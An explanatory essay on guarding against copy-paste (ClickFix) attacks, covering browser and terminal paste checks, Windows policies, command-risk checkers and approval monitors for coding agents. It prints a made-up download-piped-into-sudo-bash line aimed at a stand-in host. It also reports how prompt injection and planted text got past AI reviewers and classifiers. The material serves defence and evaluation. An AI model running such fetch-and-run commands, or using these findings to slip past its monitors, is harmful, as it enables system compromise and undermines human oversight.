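People copy private things, and many won't expect their browser to send any of them to Google. Gangwar (2026), in *Chrome can now share your clipboard data with Google servers*, raises this objection and gives Google's reply that Chrome first removes personally identifiable information. IlSoftware.it's *Chrome controlla gli appunti per bloccare potenziali comandi pericolosi* adds that Chrome doesn't check every copy indiscriminately. This is the outlet's own interpretation, but it fits Google's description, in which only suspicious commands leave the device.

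The reply is reasonable as far as it goes, but a command can be sensitive without containing anything personal. Here is a made-up example:

```
curl -H "X-Key: made-up-key-123" https://payroll.example.invalid/report
```

The line contains nobody's name, but anyone who read it would have the address of a company's payroll server and a key to it. Chrome may also remove keys, but Google has promised only to remove personal information.

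Clubic's *Chrome détecte les arnaques ClickFix que des arnaqueurs vous font copier* also notes that Google promises in its post never to log, keep or train models on the web page text it analyses, but for the clipboard mentions only the removal of personal data. This doesn't show that Google keeps the commands, but the post leaves the question open.

The feature mainly reduces privacy for people who use commands for their work, since a legitimate PowerShell command can look much like an attacker's. It seems useful even to someone who never copies commands from web pages, although Clubic concludes that such a person will gain little from it. A fake check may persuade exactly this person to copy a command for the first time, and Chrome would have almost nothing else of theirs to send.

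A browser can avoid the privacy problem by checking the text on the user's own computer. Opera has done this since July 2026 with Paste Protect, which uses built-in rules to block the copying of suspicious commands. But attackers can study these rules without Opera finding out. Google, by contrast, can change its analysis on the server at any time, and it receives any suspicious text that attackers test in Chrome with Chrome's feature turned on.

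Push Security sells a similar block to companies. Help Net Security's *Push Security detects and blocks malicious copy-and-paste activity* (2025) repeats the company's claim that it can distinguish malicious scripts from code copied from GitHub with "minimal false positives", again without a figure. Blocking stops more attacks than warning does, because the victim can't click past a block. But if the tool blocks a harmless line that a developer needs, the developer will probably retype it or open another browser.

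All these checks miss text that never passes through the browser, such as text copied from a desktop email program or an AI assistant's own application, or dictated by a caller. A check for dangerous commands is also unlikely to flag a cloud trust policy with a stranger's account number, because the policy contains no command.

### What gets lost on the clipboard

Windows and macOS label downloaded files, but plain text on the clipboard has no equivalent label. The Windows clipboard format for web content has an optional field for the page's address, but a command copied as plain text doesn't include it. When someone pastes a command, the terminal may therefore be unable to distinguish between one from an unknown website and one from the user's own notes.

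An operating system could label copied text with its source and pass the label to the terminal. This would help with ordinary ClickFix pages, and people who use a shell would notice no change until a warning appeared. But the label might reveal to other programs which pages the user had been reading, so the system would have to restrict access to it. It would also help less with shared AI conversations, because their source is a well-known company's website.

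### What a terminal can do with a paste

Bracketed paste, the feature that stops a line break in pasted text from acting as the Enter key, depends on both the shell and the terminal. The shell signals the terminal to turn it on. The terminal then sends a short code before any pasted text and another after it, and should remove any imitations of these codes from the pasted text.

Two harmless lines show the effect:

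```
echo "good morning"
echo "good night"
```

Without bracketed paste, the shell prints "good morning" as soon as the user pastes the two lines. With it, both lines stay on the command line until the user presses Enter.

This gives the user time to read the text, but the terminal doesn't assess it. It protects people who look before they press Enter, but a ClickFix page gets around it by including Enter in its instructions. It barely inconveniences experienced users, who press one more key and may see a few stray characters in older programs that don't support the codes.

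Some terminals also ask for confirmation before pasting several lines. Windows Terminal does so by default and has a separate warning for very long text. These checks only count lines and characters, so attackers can't defeat them by encoding the command. The multi-line warning could be useful against campaigns such as TerminalFix that run longer scripts in terminals, but it doesn't appear for a one-line command such as the earlier curl example. Administrators often paste whole blocks of commands, so they are the most likely to turn the warning off.

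The terminal and the shell may be on different machines. When an administrator connects to a remote server from a laptop, the laptop's terminal receives the paste, but the server runs the command. A check on the laptop can examine the text, but it may have no information about the command's rights on the server or what else is running there.

### Apple's warning

In March 2026, Apple added a warning to Terminal in macOS 26.4 that interrupts a paste before the text reaches the shell. The message describes the text as possible malware, and the user can then cancel the paste or continue.

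Apple doesn't show the warning to everyone. Early users' accounts suggested that it depended on the text, the app it came from, and whether the person regularly used Terminal. These accounts are a rough guide at best, because people were inferring the rule from a few attempts on their own Macs, and Apple can change it in any update. Aiming the warning at people who rarely open Terminal would make sense, since pasting a command is unusual for them, while regular users would soon dismiss it without reading it. But a developer who follows a fake installation guide may get no warning.

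A writer for Tom's Guide tried the warning at the end of March, reported that it worked and wanted the same protection on Windows. This small trial shows that the warning can appear when it should. Measuring how often it fails would require pasting a large set of real ClickFix commands, and a much larger set of ordinary ones, on Macs with different histories of use.

In April 2026, researchers reported a ClickFix variant that avoided Terminal. The warning is also limited to Apple's own Terminal program, so other terminals, including those built into code editors, need their own. Scammers can also tell people to click the button for pasting anyway, just as they can tell them to type the phrase that Firefox requires before pasting into its developer console.

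### Taking away the Run dialog

A company that manages its employees' computers can also restrict what pasted text can start. Such a policy doesn't depend on detecting an attack, but it also affects legitimate work, especially for people who need a shell.

The Run dialog is the simplest feature to restrict, and most of the earlier ClickFix pages sent their victims there. A Windows policy removes it from the Start menu, disables its keyboard shortcut and removes the similar command in Task Manager. Few office workers would notice the change, but administrators and support technicians would lose a quick way to open tools, which they could still find through the Start menu.

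A policy that blocks only the Run dialog doesn't stop attacks that send victims elsewhere. TerminalFix sent people to a terminal, and FileFix sent them to the file manager. The policy is still worth having for staff who don't use the dialog, because it barely affects them and makes attackers use longer or less familiar instructions.

### Allowing only approved programs

Antivirus software normally blocks programs it recognises as harmful and lets others run. With an application allow-list, the system runs only programs that a company has approved, whether by the maker's signature, the program's exact contents or the folder it is in. If a pasted command downloads an unapproved program, Windows blocks it from starting, even if no antivirus maker has seen it before.

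The allow-list is less useful at the start of the attack, because PowerShell, curl and other parts of Windows are on almost every list. A company can block some of them for employees who don't need them. If PowerShell has to stay available, Windows can run it in a restricted mode. Everyday commands still work, but scripts the company hasn't approved can't freely call the deeper Windows functions that malware tends to use.

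TerminalFix loaded its malicious library through a genuine, signed program. An allow-list that approved programs from that maker would have let it run. An allow-list can also cover libraries, but there are far more libraries than programs, and somebody has to update the list whenever legitimate software changes.

Allowing only approved programs to run inconveniences developers most. They create a new, unapproved program every time they compile their code, so the company has to exempt a folder, sign each build automatically or give them a separate machine for this work. An exempt folder is convenient, but malware can also run from it. Administrators may have to get their scripts signed before using them, which can delay urgent repairs to a failed server.

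### Scanning scripts as they run

PowerShell can pass a script's text to the installed antivirus program before running it, through a Windows feature called the Antimalware Scan Interface. This helps with encoded commands and with scripts that exist only in memory, as in Stormshield's ClickFix case, both of which are weaknesses of ordinary file scanning. PowerShell has to decode a base64 command to run it, and can then submit the decoded text.

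The antivirus program can then block text it recognises as malicious. It can't examine a second script until the first one has fetched it, and this check doesn't cover programs that don't use the interface. Python doesn't use it by default, and TerminalFix ran its last step in Python.

PowerShell's execution policy doesn't stop commands pasted at the prompt, because it controls whether PowerShell will run script files. Microsoft doesn't treat the policy as a security boundary.

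Script scanning usually causes shell users little delay. Its main drawback is false alarms, because administrators' scripts, like malicious ones, create accounts, change security settings and connect to many machines at once. If an administrator responds by exempting a whole folder of scripts, an attacker who can write to that folder can avoid scanning too.

### Fewer standing administrator rights

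A company can remove standing administrator rights, which an account has all the time, and grant them only for a particular task or a short period. This limits what a pasted command can do, but doesn't prevent someone from pasting it.

The AMOS attack on the person trying to free up disk space, for example, relied on passing the stolen password to `sudo`. By default, macOS lets only administrators use `sudo`, so the password would have failed on a standard account. The malware could still have taken the user's own data, but changing the system itself would have been much harder.

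The difference can be greater on an office network, where an attacker with only an ordinary employee's rights has to gain higher ones before shutting down the antivirus software or taking over the domain controller. That may take time, giving defenders a chance to notice, but it may also be easy. In Epe, the attacker gained the necessary rights through one poorly secured emergency account.

People who need a shell often also need administrator rights to install tools, load drivers or change network settings. If a colleague has to approve each request, they must wait. Automatic approval removes the wait, but it also approves requests from people who are following a scammer's instructions. Temporary rights work best for people who need them rarely. They give little extra protection if an engineer requests them every morning and keeps them until the evening.

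These system controls also apply to AI agents. An agent on a standard account can't use administrator rights, and an allow-list applies whether a person or an agent starts the program. Browser copy checks and terminal paste warnings don't help when an agent runs a command directly, because the command never passes through the clipboard.

### Ten thousand false warnings

Any guardrail that tries to recognise harmful text has to cope with the fact that nearly all pastes are harmless. Suppose that 100 out of 10 million pastes are harmful, and that a check catches 95% of those. Its false alarm rate is 0.1%, so it flags one harmless paste in a thousand. All figures in this calculation are invented.

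```
True warnings:     100       × 95%  = 95
False warnings:    9,999,900 × 0.1% = about 10,000
```

The check gives the right answer for about 99.9% of all pastes, and a company could truthfully advertise that. But someone who sees a warning will find that it is wrong more than 99 times out of 100. The result changes a great deal with a lower false alarm rate:

| False alarm rate | True warnings | False warnings | Share of warnings that are true |
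|---|---:|---:|---:|
| 0.1% | 95 | about 10,000 | 0.9% |
| 0.01% | 95 | about 1,000 | 9% |
| 0.001% | 95 | about 100 | 49% |

Catching every harmful paste instead of 95% of them would add only five true warnings and remove none of the false ones. For about half the warnings to be true, the false alarm rate has to be roughly as low as the share of pastes that are harmful, which is one in 100,000 in this example. The real share is unknown, and it must differ between a software company and a household.

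A rate that low is also hard to verify. If a company tests its check on 10,000 harmless commands and gets no false warnings, the true rate could still be as high as 0.03%, by the usual statistical rule of thumb. That would mean about 3,000 false warnings in 10 million pastes. A claim of "minimal false positives" is therefore hard to assess without knowing how many harmless commands were tested.

The best argument for a selective warning like Apple's is that checking only the people most at risk makes a larger share of the warnings true. Suppose 100,000 of the 10 million pastes come from people who rarely open a terminal, and these include 80 of the 100 harmful ones. If the original check, with its 0.1% false alarm rate, covers only this group, it gives 76 true warnings and about 100 false ones, so about 43% of the warnings are true. However, 24 harmful pastes get through instead of five,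 most of them from regular terminal users.

Checking in two stages, as Chrome does, can also reduce false warnings. If a first check on the device picks out 1% of the harmless pastes, it sends about 100,000 of them to the server. If the server wrongly flags 0.1% of those, users see only about 100 false warnings. In practice the server would probably do worse, because it receives the harmless commands that look most like attacks. This method also reduces privacy, because 100,000 harmless texts leave people's computers, and most of the people who pasted them would see no warning telling them so.

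Even a warning that is usually wrong can be worth showing. If each false warning takes ten seconds to dismiss, 10,000 of them take up about 28 hours of people's time, and a single serious intrusion can easily take longer to deal with. But the warnings only help if people take the true ones seriously. If four out of five people have become so used to false alarms that they click past every warning, the 95 true warnings stop only 19 attacks. Blocking the text outright would stop all 95, but it would also block 10,000 harmless commands, and some of the people who needed them would ask for the check to be turned off.

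## Can software or a second model judge whether a command is dangerous?

A checker that reads a command can try to establish whether it needs high rights, whether it could do harm, or whether it serves what the user asked for. A warning labelled "dangerous" often mixes the three, although ordinary commands show that the answers differ:

| User's request | Command | Needs administrator rights | Could do serious harm | Serves the request |
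|---|---|---|---|---|
| Refresh the list of available software | `sudo apt update` | Yes | Hardly | Yes |
| Delete the example photos | `rm -r ~/example-photos` | No | Yes | Yes |
| Free up some disk space | `rm -r ~/example-photos` | No | Yes | Probably not |
| Summarise a web page | `echo "good morning"` | No | No | No |

A checker that looks only for `sudo` would interrupt the software update but allow the command that deletes the photos. The greeting command in the last row is harmless, but summarizing a page shouldn't require a command, so the assistant may have picked it up from the page.

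Whether an action is acceptable can also depend on facts outside the command. In *Same Operation, Different Permission*, Jing, Chen and colleagues (2026) gave AI reviewers identical operations with different evidence of permission. For example, an assistant may issue a refund while it has valid delegated authority, but not after someone revokes that authority. Qwen3Guard, a model that screens text for harmful content, let through 72 of the 80 forbidden operations, presumably because the text of a refund operation contains nothing offensive. Two other models judged all 160 cases correctly, so software can judge permission if it receives the evidence.

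Whether a command is harmful also depends on the circumstances. *The Limit Is in the Input, Not the Model* (2026) tests commands for industrial machines and labels some of them harmless, but only on the assumption that the guards are intact and the safety conditions hold. A checker that receives only the command can't confirm either assumption.

### Four ways to read one line

The made-up installation command from the start of this account is a useful test for the different methods:

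```
curl -fsSL https://setup.example.invalid/fix.sh | sudo bash
```

The simplest method is a list of forbidden patterns, such as a download piped into a shell. It would flag this line if the pattern allows for `sudo` before `bash`, but it would also flag legitimate installers of the same form. Pattern matching is almost instant and always gives the same result, but whoever writes the list has to anticipate every wording. *CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) mentions a flaw in Claude Code versions before 1.0.93 that let a rewritten command get past a check meant to allow only commands that read data.

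A parser divides the line into its parts, much as the shell does. Here it would find curl with its settings and address, a pipe, `sudo` and `bash`. Liu and colleagues built a checker, also called CARE, that gives such parts risk scores and adds them up. If it classifies the example by its `sudo`, the published weights give roughly this result:

```
Pipe into a shell:             1.00 × 0.1 = 0.100
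Administrator rights (sudo):   0.75 × 0.3 = 0.225
Sensitive files named:         0.00 × 0.3 = 0.000
Total before known patterns:                0.325
```

CARE allows commands that score below 0.15, blocks those at 0.35 or above and treats the rest as doubtful. A match with one of its patterns for downloading and running code could add up to 0.3 to the score. Even without a match, CARE would probably block the line, because it blocks doubtful commands in its high-risk categories without further review. The same calculation gives `sudo apt update` a score of 0.225, and CARE apparently blocks it too, which would mean blocking a harmless command because it runs with elevated privileges.

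A trained classifier is a model that has learned from labelled examples to sort text into categories such as "safe" and "unsafe". The example looks like many known attacks, so a classifier trained on commands would probably flag it. However, the classifier may give only a label, without a reason the user could check.

A general language model can also judge commands. Given a command and a written question about it, the model can explain, for example, that the command runs a stranger's script as root. It can take the user's request into account and may recognise the address of a well-known project. It may also guess what the script does, which is risky because a fluent guess can look like knowledge.

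None of these methods checks the script's contents, because curl hasn't fetched it yet. They can detect a risky way of installing software, but they can't distinguish a legitimate script from an infostealer at that address.

### How much the checkers catch

Liu and colleagues compared these methods on 220 dangerous and 329 harmless Linux commands. Most of the dangerous ones came from a public collection of simulated attacks. The researchers also disguised each of 50 dangerous commands in five ways and mixed the resulting 250 with 250 harmless commands.

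| Method | Dangerous commands caught | Harmless commands flagged | Disguised commands caught | Harmless commands flagged in the disguise test |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| List of 22 patterns | 17% | 0% | 39% | 0.4% |
| Granite Guardian, a trained classifier | 82% | 46% | not given | 63% |
| Llama Guard 3, a trained classifier | 40% | 1.2% | not given | 4.4% |
| Language model as judge | 67% | 11% | 98% | 25% |
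| CARE without a model | 76% | 1.8% | 92% | 13% |
| CARE with a model for doubtful cases | 76% | 0.9% | 91% | 12% |

On the main test, CARE had the best balance between catching dangerous commands and allowing harmless ones, though its makers chose the test and tuned its settings on related commands. The classifiers were at a disadvantage because their developers built them to screen general text for harmful content. Granite Guardian caught the largest number of dangerous commands on the main test, but it also flagged nearly half of the harmless ones, which would make it too disruptive for daily use.

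The results on disguised commands are better than one might expect. Disguise can be a warning sign, because few people have an innocent reason to scramble a command. *ClawGuard* (2026) therefore sends heavily disguised commands to the user for approval. But the 50 commands that Liu and colleagues disguised weren't the ones in their main test, so comparing the columns doesn't show that disguise makes a command easier to catch.

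The harmless commands in the disguise test also excluded anything with `sudo`, so the test did not measure how often the checkers would interrupt administrators' legitimate privileged work. Only five of the 220 dangerous commands in the main test were in the category that downloads and runs code, which is the usual form of a copy-paste attack. CARE and the model judge each caught four of the five.

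Liu and colleagues calculate that if 100 of 10,000 commands were dangerous, CARE would stop about 76, miss 24 and block about 90 harmless ones. False alarms would therefore outnumber correct blocks here too.

A second model doesn't always improve the result. In another test, the researchers ran 600 commands that a language model had written in response to requests for attacks. Without a guard, 75% ran successfully. CARE's fixed rules reduced this to 37%, but adding a model for doubtful cases raised it to 52.5%, because the model allowed some commands that the rules had flagged. The same model had written the attacks, which may be why it allowed them.

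Jing and colleagues found the opposite problem when they combined reviewers on 1,215 access requests. On its own, their best model wrongly approved one request. Adding a second, stricter reviewer stopped that one but also blocked 171 legitimate requests. So whether a second reviewer helps depends on which errors the reviewers make, and a company can only learn this by testing them together.

### Running the command on a copy

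Software can run the command in an isolated copy of the system and check what changes, instead of judging the text. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) shows why this can matter with `make clean`, a command programmers use to remove temporary files. It carries out whatever a project's own settings file lists under "clean", so the same command can delete only temporary files in one project and the source code and its history in another.

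The Caper system first saves the state of an isolated container, then runs the command there with the network off. It records changed files, attempted connections and any passwords or keys the command reads, and condenses this into a short report. A language model compares the report with the user's task. If the model approves, Caper keeps the changes. Otherwise, Caper restores the saved state and gives the agent the reason, so the agent can try something safer.

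The test used 102 tasks in which an ordinary request made the agent run a tool that secretly deleted or overwrote a file. Each task also had a harmless version, with the same request and command but a safe tool. When the approving model read only the conversation, harm still occurred in 17.6% of the dangerous tasks, and the model blocked 61.8% of the harmless ones. With the report on what the command had done, harm fell to 7.8% and blocked harmless tasks to 1.0%.

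Lost files are an easy kind of harm for this method to detect. Caper's advantage was smaller on a broader set of 682 tasks by other researchers. Harm occurred in 6.7% of those tasks with Caper, 14.8% with the best of six existing systems and 19.7% with no approval.

In the curl example, curl can't fetch the script with the network off, so `bash` receives nothing and no files change. The report would contain little more than an attempted connection. Under Caper's instructions, the model should not treat a lack of harmful effects as proof of safety, but it still has no script to judge.

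If a company allowed the download, the script would run in the copy and its changes would appear. Caper keeps the result of an approved trial instead of running the command again, so the download server can't send a different script the second time. An administrator who tries a command on a test machine and then runs it again on a real server doesn't have this protection. A script with network access could also send out anything in the copy during the trial, before anyone has judged the script.

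Some malware also waits before acting, or checks whether it is in a test environment. Neither set of tasks included an attacker who had adapted to Caper, so Caper would probably do worse against one.

### What an assistant can put in its answer

An assistant that only gives advice can't stop a user from pasting a command, but it can make the command easier to judge. The most useful thing it can add is probably an explanation of why a command needs administrator rights. If the answer explains that installing a driver needs `sudo` but downloading the file doesn't, the user can do most of the work from an ordinary account. The assistant should mention these rights only when a command needs them, since people soon stop reading a warning that appears under every answer.

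An assistant can also state where a command came from. A label such as "This comes from a page at setup.example.invalid" gives the user a source to check. Without it, the command appears to come from the assistant's own expertise. A misled model might name the wrong source, so it would be safer for the program around the model to add the label, since that program has a record of the pages it fetched.

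An assistant can often replace a risky step with one that the user can inspect or undo. Instead of piping the example script into a shell, it could suggest saving and reading it:

```
curl -fsSL -o fix.sh https://setup.example.invalid/fix.sh
less fix.sh
```

The first line saves the script without running it, and the second displays it. If the user then runs the saved file, the server can't substitute a different script, although the script may still download more code when it runs. For other tasks, it may be safer to rename a folder instead of deleting it, or to copy a settings file before changing it. In one of Wu and colleagues' tests, Caper blocked a database update that would also have deleted three tables. The agent then made a backup and ran only the part the user needed.

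Declining to relay instructions from a page is harder, because users often want them, as when someone asks how to install a program and needs the command from its installation page. But an assistant can refuse to pass on instructions unrelated to the user's question, and tell the user that the page contained them. This would have stopped CloudSEK's hidden ClickFix lure, but not a fake installation page, whose instructions are relevant to the question.

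As a related safeguard, Claude Code runs a separate check on web pages, files and other material before the agent receives them, according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*. If something looks like an attempt to take control of the agent, the check adds a warning that the agent should return to the user's request.

### Asking a chatbot whether the command is safe

Kaspersky advises people who don't understand a set of instructions to close the page or, if the task seems important, consult someone knowledgeable. Alternatively, it suggests pasting the command into an AI chatbot and asking what the command does and whether it is dangerous. Its evidence is a screenshot of ChatGPT warning against the fake Atlas guide and the remark that ChatGPT "typically handles this task fairly well".

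No independent test of this advice seems to exist. The closest is the study by Liu and colleagues, in which a model judge, Qwen3-Coder-30B, had to answer with one word, "safe" or "dangerous". It caught two thirds of the dangerous commands and flagged about one in nine harmless ones. Qwen3-Coder-30B is much smaller than the leading models of 2026. ChatGPT may well do better, since it can also explain its reasoning and sometimes look things up.

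The advice is still worth following, as long as people rely less on an answer of "safe" than on one of "dangerous". Stopping after a "dangerous" answer does little harm, even if the answer is wrong. But at the rate Liu and colleagues measured, the chatbot would label a third of dangerous commands safe, and a chatbot that can't obtain the script can assess only the line that fetches it.

It helps to ask a chatbot about a command in a new conversation, because hidden text may have influenced the one that produced the command. The user should remove passwords and keys before pasting the command. The pasted text can still mislead the model in a new conversation, so a chatbot's approval shouldn't be the only check on a command that runs as root.

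### How coding agents decide when to ask

Agents that run commands themselves need a rule for when to stop and ask. Codex, OpenAI's current programming agent, has two separate settings, according to the company's documentation. A sandbox limits what the agent can do, such as which folders it can change and whether it can use the network. An approval policy determines when the agent has to ask, for example before it leaves the sandbox.

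The user normally answers these approval requests, but can hand them to a second agent. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) describes how this works inside OpenAI. In its illustration of 10,000 actions, 9,280 stayed within the sandbox and needed no approval. The reviewing agent approved 713 of the other 720 and rejected seven. Codex found a safer way to continue in four of the seven cases, and stopped and asked the user in the other three.

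The reviewer correctly rejected 90.3% of the actions in made-up cases where the agent went further than its user wanted. Trębacz and colleagues also found cases where text could mislead the reviewer into approving a command, and they warn against treating the reviewer as a guarantee.

In Claude Code's automatic mode, reading files and editing them within the project usually need no review, while shell commands and web requests go to a classifier unless the user has already allowed them. The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's proposed actions, but not the agent's explanations or the pages the agent has read. This prevents a persuasive explanation or a planted instruction from directly influencing the decision.

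A quick first check errs on the side of blocking, and a slower one reviews whatever the first flags. Anthropic reports that together they blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions by its own staff and missed 17% of the 52 actions in which the agent had really gone too far. The second percentage is rough because the sample is so small. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly treated it as something the user had agreed to.

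Such a check can do little to protect a user who already believes a lure. *Ajar* (2026) reports that Claude Code's automatic mode allowed every tested action when the instruction came in the user's own message. A user who pastes a fake repair guide into the agent and asks it to follow the steps has asked for the harmful command.

### Do people catch what the software misses?

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, in which the company replaced one approval prompt per session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) rejected it, while the automatic mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). According to the same source, users approve 97% of the agent's requests, but that figure alone doesn't prove carelessness, because most requests are harmless.

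People rejected about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. They stopped six commands that the software had allowed, so requiring both checks would have raised the number blocked from 937 to 943. The testers worked in an environment set up for the study and might have been more careful on their own computers. Anthropic had an interest in the result, since it was about to make the automatic mode the default for most individual users.

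The 89% applies to commands whose danger was clear from their text. In Wu and colleagues' test, where the danger was inside a tool, 62.7% of the dangerous tasks still ended in harm under the automatic mode. *Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested the mode on requests that didn't make clear what the agent was allowed to do. According to Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review?*, the mode missed 81% of the dangerous actions across 128 scenarios, partly because edits to project files never reached the classifier.

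Results for prompt injection also vary with the attacker. In an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned, none of 720 attempts succeeded against its newest models in automatic mode. *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* (Crosley, 2026) reports that the researcher Rehberger later got through in three of five runs with one method. Five runs are too few to estimate a success rate, but the three successes show that the earlier result didn't mean the models were immune.

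### Approval or isolation

An approval prompt works only if somebody judges the command correctly, but isolation limits the damage even if nobody does. Isolation also reduces the number of approval prompts, as in OpenAI's example of 9,280 actions.

Anthropic calls sandboxing safe but laborious, because someone has to configure each new capability, and access to the network or the host computer weakens it. OpenAI's *running codex safely* describes a compromise for the company's own staff. Codex can reach expected addresses, can't reach forbidden ones and has to ask about unfamiliar domains, which an agent may need when it installs packages.

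People also weaken the boundary to avoid interruptions. About 5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version have a standing rule that allows every shell command. Another 43% allow programs such as Python, which can do almost anything a shell can. Claude Code ignores such broad rules in automatic mode. OpenAI's *Auto-review* recommends allowing a specific command, such as the one that runs a project's tests, instead of every command that starts with "python" or "curl".

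Isolation should therefore come first, with approval required for the few actions that must reach outside it. Even approval prompts need care, because their text can mislead a person as well as a model. People may judge larger decisions more critically than single commands. Claude Code's users reject 39% of the plans it presents but only 3% of its individual requests. Some surely just want a different plan, but they do seem to read the plans.

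Administrators can't rely on a sandbox alone, because their work often requires changing the real system, for example by installing a driver. They can test a command in isolation first, but eventually someone has to run it with full rights. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

### A procedure for administrators

An administrator who receives a privileged command from an assistant can take these steps before running it:

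1. Write down the one change the command should make. Without this, it is easy to accept a command that is merely related to the task.

2. Find the command in the software maker's own documentation, starting from an address that didn't come from the assistant. The assistant's explanation may rest on the same false page as its command.

3. Save any script the command would download, read it and keep that copy. Running the saved copy ensures that the server can't substitute another script after the check. If the script fetches more code, check that too.

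4. Identify the part that needs administrator rights and run everything else from an ordinary account. A mistake in the other parts will then do less damage.

5. Try the saved version on an isolated copy of the server without real passwords or customer data, and compare the changes with the note from step 1. The text may not reveal what a command does on this particular system. A clean trial isn't proof, since harmful code can wait or behave differently there.

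6. Make a backup, check that it can be restored, and ask a colleague to review the command if the server matters. The colleague should get the original request and the source as well as the command, because the text alone doesn't show whether the change is wanted.

7. Record the command, its source and the time, then run the version that passed the checks. If something goes wrong weeks later, investigators will need to know what ran and where it came from.
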